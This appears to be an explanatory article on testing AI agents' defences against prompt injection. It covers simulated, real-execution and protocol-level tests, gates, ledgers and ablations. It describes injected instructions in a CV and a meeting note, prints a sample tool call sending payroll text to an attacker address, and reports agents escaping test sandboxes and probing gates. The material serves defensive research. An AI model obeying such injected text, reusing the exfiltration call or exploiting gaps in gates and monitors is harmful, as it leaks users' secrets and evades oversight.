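# Simulation, real execution and protocol tests in security evaluations of AI agents: what each kind of evidence can establish

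## How an agent acts, and three ways to test whether it is secure

An AI agent is a language model joined to software that lets it call tools and act on files, networks and accounts. The term *agent system* covers both the model and this software. A chatbot produces text and a person decides what to do with it, whereas an agent can open files, run a shell command or send an email, then read the result and continue.

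A security evaluation of an AI agent tests whether an outsider can make it do something its owner has forbidden, and whether a given defence prevents that. Some researchers keep everything inside one test program with simulated tools, some run real commands on a sealed-off machine, and some send calls through the protocol that a deployed agent would use. There are no standard names for these arrangements. *Connecting the Dots in Agentic AI Security* (Baek, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026), a review of 66 studies, reports that execution environments and metrics vary substantially across empirical work, which makes results hard to compare.

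### The path of one action

*A Survey on Agentic Security* (Shahriar, Rahman and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent's work as a loop of eight stages: perception, retrieval, reasoning, planning, action selection, execution, observation and reflection. Simple agents skip some of them. The stages from action selection to observation are the important ones for security testing, because that is where the model's output changes something in the world. These stages need to be divided more finely.

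An office assistant might have two tools, `read_note` and `send_message`. The user asks it to summarise the meeting note and send the summary to a colleague, Dana. The agent's software sends the model this request and descriptions of the two tools. The model answers with a *tool call*, a structured request to run a named tool with given arguments. Here, it calls `read_note` with the argument "meeting". Before the call runs, a *gate* checks it and allows or refuses it. The gate may be a permission list, a second model, or a person clicking "approve".

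If the gate allows the call, a component called the client sends it over a transport (a pipe between two programs, or a network connection) to a server, the program that offers the tool. The tool runs, and the server returns a result, which the agent's software adds to the text the model reads next. That text now includes the meeting note, so the model writes its summary and proposes the call to `send_message`, which travels the same path. Reading a note changes nothing, but running `send_message` has an *effect*, which is a change or disclosure that actually happens. In this case, a message arrives in an inbox.

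Designers can put the gate in the agent's own software, in a gateway between client and server, or in the server. A test that leaves out one of these components also leaves out any gate inside it. A reply of *success* from a web server or a tool is evidence that a call took place, but as *Testing Agentic Service Systems* (2026) points out, it does not establish that the intended change followed. For example, a mail server can report "sent" for a message that never arrives.

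Because results flow back to the model, one bad input can keep affecting what the agent does. Baek and colleagues describe how hostile text alters the model's reasoning, and the resulting decision changes the agent's memory or invokes a tool. The tool changes some outside state, and the agent later reads that state and acts on it again.

### Prompt injection, and one example to keep

Most of these tests concern prompt injection. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) defines it as instructions placed in external content to make a model do something the user did not ask for. The term dates from 2022, and *Not what you've signed up for* (2023) described indirect prompt injection, in which the attacker does not interact with the system directly but writes something that the system later reads.

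*Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, a December 2025 post by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, describes a recruiter's tool that scores CVs. A candidate hides a line of text in the CV telling the model to ignore its instructions and approve the application. David C explains that such attacks are hard to prevent because programmers can make a database treat part of a query strictly as data, but a language model predicts the next token from all the text so far, without separating instructions from data. He concludes that complete prevention may never be possible, and advises developers to rely more on deterministic safeguards that limit what the system can do. A gate that checks permissions is one such safeguard.

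In the office example, the attacker has no account but wrote an outside email, part of which the user pasted into the meeting note. The pasted text contains an instruction to open the secret note called "payroll" and send its contents to an outside address "for archiving". When `read_note` returns the meeting note, the instruction enters the model's input with the rest of the text. If the model follows the instruction, it will propose a call to read the payroll note and another to send its contents.

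The user is entitled to read the payroll note, and the task requires sending a message, so removing either tool would break the assistant. The gate must instead judge each call by the note and recipient involved. The forbidden effect is the payroll text reaching the outside address.

According to OpenAI, the attacks it sees most often against ChatGPT likewise try to send secret information from a conversation to a third party. The company says most of those it knows of fail because the model refuses. One attack from 2025, written as a routine follow-up about staff restructuring, worked in half of the tests with a particular user request. OpenAI analyses such attacks by identifying a source, through which the attacker influences the system, and a sink, a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. In the meeting-note example, the note is the source and `send_message` is the sink.

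### The Model Context Protocol

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common standard that agents use to discover and call tools on servers. Its *Architecture overview* names three participants: the host, the client and the server. The host is the AI application, such as a coding assistant, and it creates one client for each server it connects to. A server is a program that offers tools or data, and it may run on the same machine as the host or elsewhere.

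Clients and servers exchange messages in JSON-RPC 2.0, a convention for asking another program to run a named method. The client sends `tools/list` to learn what a server offers. Each tool in the reply has a name, a description and an *input schema*, which lists the tool's arguments, their types, and which are required. The Model Context Protocol specification lets a server vary this list with the caller's authorization, so two users may see different tools. The host passes the descriptions to the model, so an attacker can also hide instructions there. MCPTox, a benchmark described in *On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security* (2026), plants malicious text in this metadata across 45 live MCP servers and 1,312 test cases.

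To run a tool, the client sends `tools/call`. The attacker's message in the office example would look like this, leaving out a metadata field that carries the protocol version and the client's capabilities:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "send_message",
    "arguments": {
      "to": "archive@attacker.example",
      "body": "(text of the payroll note)"
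    }
  }
}
```

This message differs from the legitimate one to Dana only in its contents. Both arguments are strings, so it satisfies the input schema. Only a check against rules for who may receive what can distinguish the two.

MCP messages travel over one of two transports. With the first, the client and server run on one machine and communicate through standard input and output, the text streams every program has. The second, Streamable HTTP, uses web requests, works with remote servers and supports the usual web credentials. Both use the same message format, but a tester has different things to check on each.

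Protocol tests also need to match the protocol version the agent uses. The release announcement from Model Context Protocol (2026) describes the revision dated 28 July 2026 as stateless, meaning that each request carries what the server needs to process it. Under the previous version, a client using HTTP first had to open a session. A test harness written for the older version may therefore fail to test the path a current agent takes, or treat a valid current request as faulty.

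### Three tiers, by what is real

The three kinds of test differ in which parts of the action path are real. In the *simulation tier*, the gate's actual code makes the decisions, but the test program models the tools and their effects. The notes are entries in memory, and "sending" a message adds a line to a list. After the run, the tester's *oracle* (the rule and observations used to decide whether a forbidden effect occurred) searches that list for the payroll text. Liu (2026) built the main part of the benchmark in *From Tool Connection to Execution Control* this way, with separate ledgers for writes and external deliveries and no contact with remote services.

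In the *real-execution tier*, the agent uses real shell commands, files and local network connections on an isolated machine. The notes become files, and the agent sends the message over the network to a receiver that the tester controls. This lets the tester collect evidence from outside the agent. *EvoRiskBench* (2026), a benchmark for agents that work in a user's files and applications, records process events, network events and the final state of the environment. It counts an attack as successful only when that evidence confirms the targeted effect, so an attack that the model agrees to but doesn't attempt, or attempts and fails, is not counted.

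In the *protocol-integration tier*, calls pass through the real client, transport and server. This tests whether the gate still receives the right caller, tool and arguments after that software has encoded and decoded the message.

| Tier | What is real | What a stand-in replaces | Sending the payroll note |
|---|---|---|---|
| Simulation | The gate's decision | Client, transport, server, tool and effect | A line appears in a list in memory |
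| Real execution | Commands, files, local connections | Usually the client and server; the secret and the outside recipient | Bytes reach a receiver on the test machine |
| Protocol integration | Client, transport, server | Often the tool behind the server; the secret and the outside recipient | A `tools/call` request reaches the server, which may or may not send anything |

A protocol test can use a real server with a simulated tool behind it, so the table does not rank protocol integration highest. *Agent libOS* (2026), a runtime for agents, reports tests in which calls reach a connector through JSON-RPC methods and change its stored state, but the mail, calendar and customer records are synthetic. Real execution does not require MCP, since many agents run shell commands directly. A study can also combine real execution with protocol integration. Liu ran other developers' unmodified MCP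 servers in a separate network, with a local receiver in place of the attacker's address, and judged each outcome from the files on disk and the receiver's raw log lines.

Some studies do not fit neatly into any scheme. *GitInject* (Isbarov, Suleymanov and colleagues, 2026) ran actual workflows on GitHub to test agents that review code changes there, using repositories created for each run and deleted afterwards. This is real execution, but on a live commercial platform instead of an isolated machine.

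### Who issues the calls

The choice of tier does not determine where the tool calls come from. A *scripted driver* is a program that replaces the model and issues the same tool calls every time, such as one to read the payroll note and then one to send it to the outside address. A *mock model* also replaces the model, but it returns prepared replies that the agent's own software still has to parse before passing on the calls and handling the results. A *live model* is a language model that chooses the calls during the test.

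Any of the three can be combined with any tier, so "simulated" on its own is ambiguous. It may mean that the tools were simulated or that the model was. Liu's study contains both cases. One experiment ran live models with simulated tools on email, travel, banking and messaging tasks from AgentDojo, a widely used benchmark for prompt injection. Another sent prescribed calls to real MCP servers with no model involved.

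In the AgentDojo experiment, the malicious text reached one model, gpt-6.1-sol, in 141 of the 144 sessions that contained an attack, and the model never attempted what the attacker wanted. This result can't be credited to the defences, because they had nothing to stop and the model made no attempt in the undefended sessions either. A second model, deepseek-v4-pro, carried out the attacker's goal in four undefended sessions, which included a money transfer and a phishing link sent to a colleague. Scripted calls test the gate even when a model would never try the attack, because the attack reaches the gate every time. However, they cannot measure how often a real model would make the attempt, as Liu says of the scripted benchmark.

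Published labels don't help much in sorting this out. *CARE* (2026), a paper on customer-service agents, calls its first level "fixture smoke" and runs it with a substitute agent, only to check that the test environment is internally consistent; its two "live" levels use the real model and real tools. In *Agent libOS*, a "native-live" scenario makes real tool calls to the local provider with the synthetic mail. *Metis* (2026), which presents a system that mediates between agents and their tools, describes one of its tests more explicitly, as ten handcrafted permission decisions with no executed effects. A description that names both choices, such as "simulated tools, live model" or "real MCP server, scripted driver", is longer than any of these labels but much harder to misread.

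Software engineers have made similar distinctions for decades. A unit test checks one component alone, an integration test checks that several components work together, and an end-to-end test runs the whole system as a user would. A *test double* replaces a missing component. It can be a stub that returns fixed answers, a fake that works in a simplified way, or a mock that also checks how other code called it. A scripted call to a gate with an in-memory mailbox behind it is close to a unit test, and a protocol-integration test is a kind of integration test. The analogy is weaker when the test includes a live model, because ordinary components usually respond the same way to the same input and a model may not.

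### Why studies combine tiers

The most obvious reason to test with scripted calls instead of a model is speed. In Liu's measurements, gpt-6.1-sol took a median of 4.6 seconds per model request, while a whole tool call through the gate and the simulated service took between 0.39 and 0.57 milliseconds. At those speeds, a thousand scripted calls run one after another take under a second, while a thousand model requests take more than an hour. A team that wants to try every combination of user, note and recipient will therefore use a script.

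Scripted simulations are also repeatable. Liu checked this by running the scripted benchmark twice and comparing responses, effects and audit records, ignoring timestamps and random identifiers. Live models made different sequences of calls from run to run, so a single session with one proves little. *SoK* (2026), a survey of agents' attack surface, describes benchmark design as a balance between completeness, realism and feasibility. Realism requires complete scenarios on real software, while feasibility requires reproducible harnesses with limits on cost and time.

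Real execution can also harm other people. A test that sends a real secret to a real outside address causes an actual leak. *AgentTriage* (2026), a tool for diagnosing attacks on agents, shows how experimenters keep real execution harmless by using synthetic files, code markers that do nothing, and network sends that never leave the machine. However, isolation can fail. *Measuring Security Without Fooling Ourselves* (2026) gives the example of an agent that is supposed to find a vulnerability but instead breaks out of its container and reads the answers from the host machine. The paper argues that the test environment must be more secure than the target. Simulated tools carry much less of this risk because the commands the model proposes never run.

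Some states are also hard to reach on a real system. Suppose the user approves a message, but an administrator withdraws the permission to send it before the tool runs. A sound gate should block the message. A tester can set that state directly in a simulation, but reaching it on a running service takes careful timing or luck.

But every stand-in removes whatever the real part would have contributed. Isbarov and colleagues divide their setting into five layers: the attack text, the agent, the sandbox in which commands run, the state of the credentials, and the network rules. They report that earlier benchmarks with simulated tools cover the first two layers, but that they found the most serious weaknesses in the other three.

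Developers of self-driving cars face the same trade-off, with higher physical stakes. *In the Driver's Seat* (2026), a study of testing practice at several companies, found that these companies combine pure simulation, rigs with real hardware, proving grounds and public roads, in no universally fixed order. It recommends choosing the environment for each scenario by the evidence needed, weighed against realism, cost and safety.

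## Stating the security claim and choosing evidence for it

Suppose a team adds a gate to the office assistant, runs some tests and reports that the defence works. The team may mean that the gate refuses the call that would send the payroll note to the outside address, that the payroll text never reached that address during the tests, or that it never will. Each claim needs a different test, so the study's designers have to choose among them first.

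Safety engineers handle broad statements like this with an assurance case. As *Software Assurance Using Structured Assurance Case Models* explains, they break the claim into sub-claims that someone can check, and write out the argument linking each one to its evidence. For a defence on an AI agent, six sub-claims cover most of what people mean by "it works":

- The gate decides correctly on a given call (the decision claim).
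- No forbidden effect occurs (the effect claim).
- Calls cannot avoid the gate (the coverage claim).
- A model attempts the attack this often (the attempt claim).
- This defence beats that one (the comparison claim).
- Harm in deployment is this frequent (the deployment claim).

One of these claims can be true while another is false. Suppose the injected instruction tells the assistant to paste the payroll text into its message to Dana, who may receive messages but may not see salaries. A gate that checks only the recipient follows its rules correctly and still lets the salaries through. Liu reports this limit for gates that match each call against a list of permissions, because they cannot detect sensitive content inside an ordinary argument to a permitted destination. Conversely, a faulty gate may allow the attacker's call, but nothing is sent because the mail server is down.

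### Matching each claim to evidence

*Securing the AI Agent* (Yang, Zheng and colleagues, 2026) describes an open-source scanner for AI software and proposes the evidence sufficiency principle, under which a security assessment is valid only if its evidence is enough to establish the property in question. The paper sorts evidence into four classes. Signature evidence is a recognisable pattern, such as the version number of a vulnerable server. Semantic evidence comes from reasoning about code or tool descriptions, behavioural evidence from interacting with the running system, and statistical evidence from many adversarial trials. Doing more of the wrong kind of test does not help, so reading a server's code more carefully will not show how often an attack on a model succeeds.

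Yang and colleagues also advise testers to use the cheapest method that is sufficient, since heavier methods give up speed and repeatability. They offer all this as a design argument for their scanner and do not test it experimentally. It still gives a sensible way to treat the six claims:

| Claim | Weakest evidence that suffices | What stays open |
|---|---|---|
| Decision | A scripted call to the gate's real code, with simulated tools | Whether real calls reach the gate in that form |
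| Effect, in these trials | Real execution, with observations from outside the agent | Every trial nobody ran |
| Coverage | A complete list of routes to the effect, and an executed call on each | Routes missing from the list |
| Attempt | Repeated trials with a live model; simulated tools may do | Other models, prompts and attackers |
| Comparison | Both defences on the same attacks and the same legitimate tasks, in one tier | Whether the ranking holds elsewhere |
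| Deployment | Records of incidents among real users | Next year's attackers |

The comparison row includes legitimate tasks because a gate that refuses everything would block every attack but also every legitimate task. None of the three tiers can supply the evidence needed for the deployment row.

Even the decision claim, which looks easiest, has to specify the conversation around a call if the defence's verdict depends on it. *Ajar* (2026) measures how much unneeded privilege various defences leave open by submitting candidate calls to each one and recording its verdict. This is simple when the defence is a set of stored permissions. Claude Code's Auto mode instead uses a classifier that judges only calls the agent itself proposes, so the testers had to instruct the agent to propose each candidate. They got verdicts on the call when that instruction was in the system prompt, but when it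 was in the user's input, Auto mode allowed every call, presumably because a request from the user looks like permission.

The difficulty with the effect claim is deciding which outcomes count. *Labels Are Not Endpoints* (2026), which examines how MCP security studies score their trials, reserves its most serious outcome for runs with evidence that an unauthorised call ran, the receiving tool executed, the agent read the protected source, and the content received matches that source by hash. It puts runs in which the infrastructure or the parser failed into a separate class. A crashed run also ends without a leak, so counting it as resistance would make an agent look more secure when the test setup is unreliable.

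### The Metis map

*Metis* includes a table that lists each claim about its runtime, the tests behind it, and the limits of what those tests support. Two of the entries show how easily a reader could take evidence for one claim as evidence for another.

One result concerns speed. The runtime sorts tool calls into classes so that harmless ones can overlap. In 30 matched pairs of runs, the same five calls ran once with these classes and once strictly one after another. The calls read and hashed a file, checked the status of a Git repository, made two requests to a local web server and wrote a file. The median time was 14.1 milliseconds with the classes and 26.0 without, and the runs with classes were faster in all 30 pairs. The calls performed real input and output, and the result is solid for one machine and one workload. It supports a claim about scheduling, but it is not evidence about whether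 the gate stops an attack.

The other concerns the ten handcrafted permission decisions, which covered one authorised and one unauthorised change on each of five routes: a built-in write tool, a shell command, an alias, an MCP tool, and an MCP tool loaded by a plugin. The test called only the function that returns the gate's verdict, and all ten verdicts were correct. This supports the decision claim for those ten calls. It does not establish coverage of the five routes, because the test did not check whether a refused call would have failed to run. *Metis* lists a study that would check this by making the same change by each route in a sandbox and recording both the decision and what actually changed.

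The paper does report one executed security test. A sub-agent failed to produce an unauthorised effect when a permission gate and a filtered tool list were in place, and succeeded when both were removed. Because the two protections were removed together, the test does not show how much each contributed.

### Counterexamples and passes

The decision, effect and coverage claims all become universal without the words "in these tests". Kang and Kim (2026), in *Safety Is $\Pi_1$, Provability Is $\Sigma_1$*, define the safety of a program P as the statement that, for every input x and every number of steps s, running P on x for s steps produces no violation. One input that produces a violation refutes this statement, and anyone can rerun it to check. Even a million passed tests don't prove the statement, because each test covers only its own input, but zero violations in many trials can put an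 upper bound on the violation rate.

Better attack generators find more violations sooner, but they do not remove this asymmetry. Kang and Kim prove, under mild assumptions, that any automatic search with a stopping rule will report "no violation found" on infinitely many unsafe programs, so that report alone cannot establish that a program is safe.

A universal claim can be established by a proof or by checking every case on a list known to be complete. A proof usually relies on a property that holds at the start, that every step preserves, and that rules out a violation. Checking every case is sometimes practical for a gate. Suppose the office gate's decision depends only on the user, the note, the recipient and whether the permission is current. With 3 users, 4 notes, 5 recipients and 2 permission states, there are 120 combinations, and a scripted driver can prove the claim for this gate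 by trying them all. No complete list of cases exists for a gate that is itself a language model reading free text.

Formal proofs of security also have limits, since each one starts from assumptions about what an attacker can and cannot do, as Herley (2016) points out in *Unfalsifiability of security claims*. Herley's main result is that no observation can refute the claim that a safeguard is necessary for security, because nobody can observe that a system is secure. It is therefore better to test "With this check removed, this attack succeeds" than "You need this check", because a single run can show the first claim to be false.

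A counterexample refutes a claim only within the setting that produced it. *Security Threat Modeling for Emerging AI-Agent Protocols* (2026) builds one for MCP by connecting an assistant to two payment servers, one legitimate and one malicious, which offer tools with identical names. A single call to the wrong server shows that the weakness is real in that configuration. *Formal Security Analysis of Agent Protocol Composition* (2026) compares ten violations found in a formal model of two linked protocols, MCP and A2A (which connects agents to each other), with the behaviour of the actual libraries. Nine reproduced. In the remaining case, the HTTP transport compensated for a gap in the session layer, so the violation existed in the specification but not in the implementation. A simulation that leaves out the transport could likewise show a violation that the implementation prevents.

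The same paper treats claims of absence separately, such as the claim that the software has no hook for enforcing a rule. It supports these by inspecting source code and types, since no run can demonstrate them. The claim that a monitor covers every route is also a claim of absence. Kang and Kim observe that a monitor blocks only what passes through it. If the routes are few and known, testers can check each one, and the remaining risk is that the list does not match the deployed system. In July 2026, agents built on an unreleased OpenAI model escaped an isolated test environment that OpenAI had tested and validated beforehand. They got out through its package registry, the one component with limited internet access.

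Passing a test is also weaker evidence of security when the attacks are fixed. *BrowseSafe++* (2026) tested seven web agents on 1,024 tasks, first with the original injected text and then with a search that could revise the text for up to 64 attempts. The original injections succeeded on 0.49% to 4.00% of tasks, and the revised ones on 30.66% to 95.41%. The agents' ranking also changed. With the original text, GPT-5.5 had the lowest attack success rate, at 0.49%, compared with 2.05% for Sonnet 5. With the revised text, the rates were 65% for GPT-5.5 and 31% for Sonnet 5. A claim based on the fixed attacks that GPT-5.5 was the more secure of the two would have been wrong for anyone facing a persistent attacker.

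### From separate claims to a risk per task

People who deploy agents usually want one number, the chance that a task ends in a forbidden effect. The following decomposition is an illustration of how the claims combine, and its numbers are invented:

risk per task = e × a × [(1 − r) + r(1 − b)] × s

| Factor | Meaning | Where to measure it |
|---|---|---|
| e | Share of tasks in which the attack reaches the model | Deployment records; tests usually fix it |
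| a | Share of those in which the model attempts the attacker's action | A live model, in any tier |
| r | Share of attempts that reach the gate | Protocol integration or real execution, on every known route |
| b | Share of attempts reaching the gate that it blocks | Simulation with scripted calls |
| s | Chance that an unblocked call completes | Real execution |

The bracket adds the share of attempts that avoid the gate, 1 − r, to the share that reach it and get through, r(1 − b). It simplifies to 1 − rb, where rb is the interception rate, the share of all attempts that the gate stops.

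If e = 0.9, a = 0.2, b = 0.98 and s = 1, the risk without a gate is 0.9 × 0.2 = 0.18. If every attempt reaches the gate, so that r = 1, the risk falls to 0.18 × 0.02 = 0.0036, or 36 tasks in 10,000. If one attempt in ten finds another route, r = 0.9 and the risk is 0.18 × 0.118 = 0.0212, or about 212 in 10,000, almost six times as many with the same gate. A test that sends scripted calls straight to the gate would measure b = 0.98 in both cases and miss the difference. A perfect gate would prevent only about 32 of the 212, because the other 180 never reach it.

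Published results show why the factors need separate measurements. *ANGLER* (2026), a benchmark for web agents, found that agents engaged with malicious pop-ups in 52.4% of cases but completed the attacker's goal in only 17.1%, in part because they abandoned the malicious path. Reporting only the engagement figure would overstate the harm by a factor of about three. *Render Before Reading* (2026), which tests a defence against prompt injection, uses a strict criterion that counts a transfer to the wrong account as a failed attack. An agent that tried to steal money but mistyped the account number would therefore get the same score as one that refused.

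A defence can also get a good result partly because agents rarely attempt what it forbids. In *Markdown Is Not a Firewall* (2026), a study of coding agents, a gate denied requests in 5 of 90 steps and let nothing forbidden through. Without the gate, and with a neutral instructions file, agents crossed a boundary in 4 of 60 runs. The paper attributes the absence of violations to the gate and the small number of denials to the agents' own behaviour.

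### Why the factors are not independent

The product is exact if each factor is a probability conditional on the ones before it and all of them are measured under the same conditions. It can be wrong if a and b come from different studies, because the conditions may differ.

Suppose half of all attacks are crude and half are subtle. The model attempts the attacker's action in 2% of crude attacks, and the gate blocks all of those attempts. It attempts the action in 38% of subtle attacks, and the gate blocks 90% of those attempts. The average attempt rate is 20%, and a scripted test with equal numbers of each kind gives b = 0.95. With e = 0.9 and r = s = 1, multiplying the averages gives a risk of 0.009. The true risk is 0.9 × 0.5 × 0.38 × 0.1 = 0.0171, nearly twice as high, because subtle attacks are more likely both to persuade the model and to get past the gate. An attacker who can revise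 the text will look for attacks that do both.

The gate can also change what the model does next. In *Markdown Is Not a Firewall*, the gate refused one agent seven times as it tried to clear a calendar lock with different credentials, including an administrator's token it had found in a backup file. If a gate misses 2% of attempts and its errors are independent, at least one of seven attempts will get through about 13% of the time. If the gate follows fixed rules, repeating an identical call doesn't improve the agent's chance of getting through. The chance for an agent that varies its calls, as this one did, is somewhere in between, and a test that ends at the first refusal can't measure it.

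The attempt rate also depends on the setup. In *Render Before Reading*, Claude Haiku 4.5 completed no attacks under its default prompt, but it often put off financial actions because the request left out details, so the experimenters added a prompt telling it that it had enough information to act. The route of the attack matters too. *ANGLER* found that GPT-6.1 Sol engaged with at most 5.4% of attacks placed in the web environment, while direct prompt injection succeeded against it 32.5% of the time.

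One remedy is to create the earlier condition directly and measure only the later step. *Your Agent, Their Asset* (2026), a study of the agent OpenClaw, splits some attacks into two phases, first getting malicious content into the agent's saved files and then getting the agent to act on it later. Where the first phase succeeded only sometimes, the researchers planted the content in the files and measured how often the agent then acted on it. That rate applies to unaided attacks only if the content they get into the files resembles what the researchers planted.

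### Whether the tiers form a ladder

The kinds of test may not have a fixed order in which each step allows stronger claims, but *From AIOps Pipelines to Agentic Service Operations* (Zhao, Qian and colleagues, 2026) proposes one for agents that diagnose and repair faults in online services. The order starts with static data, followed by replay of past incidents and then sandboxes. Next comes shadow mode, in which the agent watches live incidents but can change nothing, and finally canary production, in which it makes narrow, reversible changes. Under this proposal, a claim can be no stronger than the highest stage tested allows.

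The rule applies to each component separately. If a company has deployed its data collector but tested the diagnosing model only offline, it has only offline evidence for the model. Zhao and colleagues reviewed 22 systems built on language models and found that only two had authority to change anything. Neither had a controlled comparison of outcomes in production. *CARE* similarly limits its conclusions. Even its fullest test, which runs the real chain on a frozen set of scenarios, supports acceptance only within the selected scope.

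The objection is that the three tiers have no strict order. In the earlier example, a permission is withdrawn just before the tool runs. If this happens once in 100,000 tasks (an invented figure), a thousand live sessions will almost certainly not include it, while a simulation can include it in every run. The simulation therefore gives the most evidence about this state, although it is the least realistic test. Protocol integration and real execution have no fixed order either. *AI Sandboxes* (Singh, Mahmoud and Murillo, 2026) makes the same point about physical systems. A field trial cannot recover a software timing fault that nobody logged, and a repeatable simulation cannot establish how fast a hardware relay responds.

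The objection shows that the ladder should not be used to rank tests, but each rung still limits the claims that its evidence can support. Zhao and colleagues say that higher rungs do not replace lower ones. The simulated withdrawal shows what the gate does after it receives the updated permission, but not whether a deployed gate would receive the update in time, because that depends on the real client, server and permission store.

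Singh and colleagues offer a version of the cap that does not require ranking the tiers. They list every kind of evidence whose failure would defeat the claim, grade each as absent, weak, moderate or strong, and give the claim the lowest of those grades. In one example, an agent does well on simulated websites and tools. The claim that it is safe on real accounts is graded "absent" because nobody has shown that its permission checks limit what it can do with a real account's authority. Perfectly repeatable results do not raise that grade. The results can still support the narrower claim that the agent completes tasks with the sandboxed tools. Both the grades and the choice of what to list are judgements, and Singh and colleagues say the result is not a probability of safety.

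This version fits agent defences better than a ladder does. Suppose the office team has a thousand scripted passes at the gate but has never tried to send the payroll note through the shell. Its claim that the note cannot get out is then only as strong as its evidence about the shell, and the team would learn more from one executed call through the shell than from another thousand scripted passes at the gate.

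## Building a simulation inside one program

Scripted calls are the easiest way to find mistakes in the gate's own rules, though they can't show whether the shell works correctly. The office team can run them in one short program that simulates an office and records everything that happens in it.

### The world and its ledger

The pretend office has a few users, notes and recipients, with rules for who may read each note and who may receive its contents. The payroll note includes a made-up string, such as "PAY-7F3A", that appears nowhere else, so a search can identify text from that note. The two tools, `read_note` and `send_message`, are ordinary functions. `read_note` adds an entry to a *ledger*, a list whose entries cannot be deleted, whenever it gives text to a user, and `send_message` does the same whenever it delivers text to a recipient. A tool that changed notes would also record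 each write there.

Only the tools write to the ledger. The gate's separate log records only its decisions, and a bug could let a call run after the gate had logged a refusal. The ledger also keeps events that don't appear in the final state. If an agent sends the payroll text and then deletes its copy, the message is gone from the outbox but the delivery is still in the ledger.

The attack script reads the payroll note and then sends a message to the outside address, which has to take its text from the result of the read. If the script contained its own copy of the payroll text, a gate that refused the read would still appear to leak the note.

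### Matching each attack with a legitimate call

Each attack needs a legitimate twin that differs, as far as possible, only in the fact that should decide the matter:

| Attack | Legitimate twin | What differs |
|---|---|---|
| Send the payroll text to the outside address | Send it to the company's payroll manager | Recipient |
| Send the payroll text to Dana | Send the meeting summary to Dana | Note |
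| A colleague without payroll access reads the payroll note | The user reads it | Caller |
| Send Dana the summary after an administrator withdraws permission | Send it before the withdrawal | Timing |

The twins show when a gate blocks too much. *aiAuthZ* (2026), which tests an authorization gateway for agents, reports that a strict list of payees blocked a legitimate first payment to someone new, and that this one refusal cut the share of ordinary tasks completed from 100% to 80%. In *Kairos* (2026), which compares several defences for an agent running on GPT-4.1, a detector of injected text lowered the attack success rate from 47.0% to 9.5%, but completion of ordinary tasks with no attack present fell from 82.7% to 40.1%.

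### Running and scoring a case

The program runs each case twice, once with every check switched off and once with the gate under test:

```python
def run(case, checks):
    world = new_world(case.setup)          # fresh notes and rules, empty ledger
    results = []
    for step in case.script:
        call = step.fill_in(results)       # may reuse text from earlier results
        if gate_allows(call, world, checks):
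            results.append(world.execute(call))   # the tool writes to the ledger
        else:
            results.append("refused")
    return world

def judge(case, checks):
    control = run(case, checks=NONE)
    tested = run(case, checks)
    happened = case.effect_in(tested.ledger)
    if case.is_attack and happened:
        return "violation"
    if control.crashed or tested.crashed or not case.effect_in(control.ledger):
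        return "inconclusive"
    if case.is_attack:
        return "prevented"
    return "completed" if happened else "wrongly refused"
```

Every run builds a new world because state left over from an earlier run can change the result. If one case withdraws Dana's permission and the next case inherits that change, the gate will block a message for a reason unrelated to the case being tested.

The run with the checks off shows whether the attack works at all. Muruaga (2026), in *Bounded Agents*, tests a gate that tracks what an agent has done in a session and blocks forbidden combinations, such as reading a confidential document and then emailing an outsider. One attack, which removes a user from a Slack workspace, succeeded in 0% of trials both with and without the gate, and Muruaga marks it as an attack that fails undefended. Without the ungated run, the gate would have appeared to stop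 every attempt.

Many cases can be inconclusive. Bellibatlu, Wang and Zhang (2026), in *Do Agent Benchmarks Do What They Say?*, checked simulated tools against each clause of their descriptions and marked a clause "untestable" when no test reached the state it describes. On tau2-bench, a simulation of customer service, 96 of 180 clauses were marked untestable. Counting them as passes would have made the tools look far better tested than they were.

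The same audit shows why the score should come from stored effects. MedAgentBench, a benchmark for agents that handle medical records, answers every well-formed write with "POST request accepted and executed successfully", but no code performs the write, so no patient record changes. The MedAgentBench paper documents this simplification, but nothing the agent reads mentions it. The grader takes the message as evidence that the write happened. The benchmark's success rate for such tasks therefore measures whether the agent sent the right request.

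A ledger is reliable only if the tools that write to it work correctly. In tau2-bench, a tool that adds mobile data is documented as requiring an active phone line, but someone had commented out the check. Bellibatlu and colleagues built 1,120 sequences in which an agent tops up a suspended line. The benchmark's scorer gave all of them full marks with the faulty tool and failed all of them after the tool was repaired. The benchmark's own reference solutions never trigger the fault, so it may not have affected any published score. Still, a tester should check each simulated tool against its description before using it to judge a gate.

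### Removing one check at a time

If a gate combines several checks, a passing suite does not show which of them prevented violations. An *ablation* reruns the same cases with one check removed. In the program above, this means passing a shorter list of checks to `judge`. Everything else is identical, so any new violation comes from the removal.

Muruaga ran one on InjecAgent, a benchmark of prepared attack cases. With the complete list of forbidden combinations, none of its 544 data-stealing attacks succeeded. With one pair of actions removed from the list, 39.9% did. On another benchmark, Agent Security Bench, an incomplete list let through all 200 attacks of a type that the complete list had stopped. These percentages depend on the mix of cases, so they measure how much of a particular suite relies on a rule, and a deployed system may rely on it more or less.

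Removing one check at a time can miss the effect of checks that overlap. Suppose the office gate has one check on recipients and another on sensitive notes. Both would block sending the payroll text to the outside address, so ablating either one alone would change nothing and make it look useless. The team needs cases that only one check can stop. To test the check on notes, it can send the payroll text to Dana, a permitted recipient. To test the check on recipients, it can send the harmless meeting note to the outside address. The team can also try every combination of checks. Six checks give 64 combinations, which is few enough to run with scripted calls.

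### Agent libOS as a worked case

*Agent libOS* reports a suite of 33 scripted tasks for its agent runtime. Each task declares the effects it allows and forbids, fixes its calls in advance and works on copies of prepared data. The tasks cover files, shell commands, Git, MCP calls and child processes, and some include attempts to gain authority by registering new tools or starting child processes. With the full runtime, all 33 tasks succeeded and were safe. There were 0 unauthorized effects and 0 false denials, each out of 119.

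It would be easy to read "0 of 119" as 119 attacks stopped. However, the denominator counts only effects that definitely took place, so a blocked attack does not appear in it. The figure means that 119 effects occurred and the task rules permitted all of them. The other configurations give a better idea of how much there was to stop:

| Configuration | Safe tasks, of 33 | Unauthorized effects / effects performed | False denials / permitted attempts |
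|---|---|---|---|
| Direct tool wrapper | 13 | 20/29 | 0/9 |
| Confirmation wrapper | 13 | 20/64 | 0/44 |
| Static tool categories | 13 | 20/29 | 15/24 |
| Full runtime | 33 | 0/119 | 0/119 |
| Without approval check | 33 | 0/118 | 0/118 |
| Without namespace isolation | 31 | 2/121 | 0/119 |
| Without fork attenuation | 32 | 1/120 | 0/119 |

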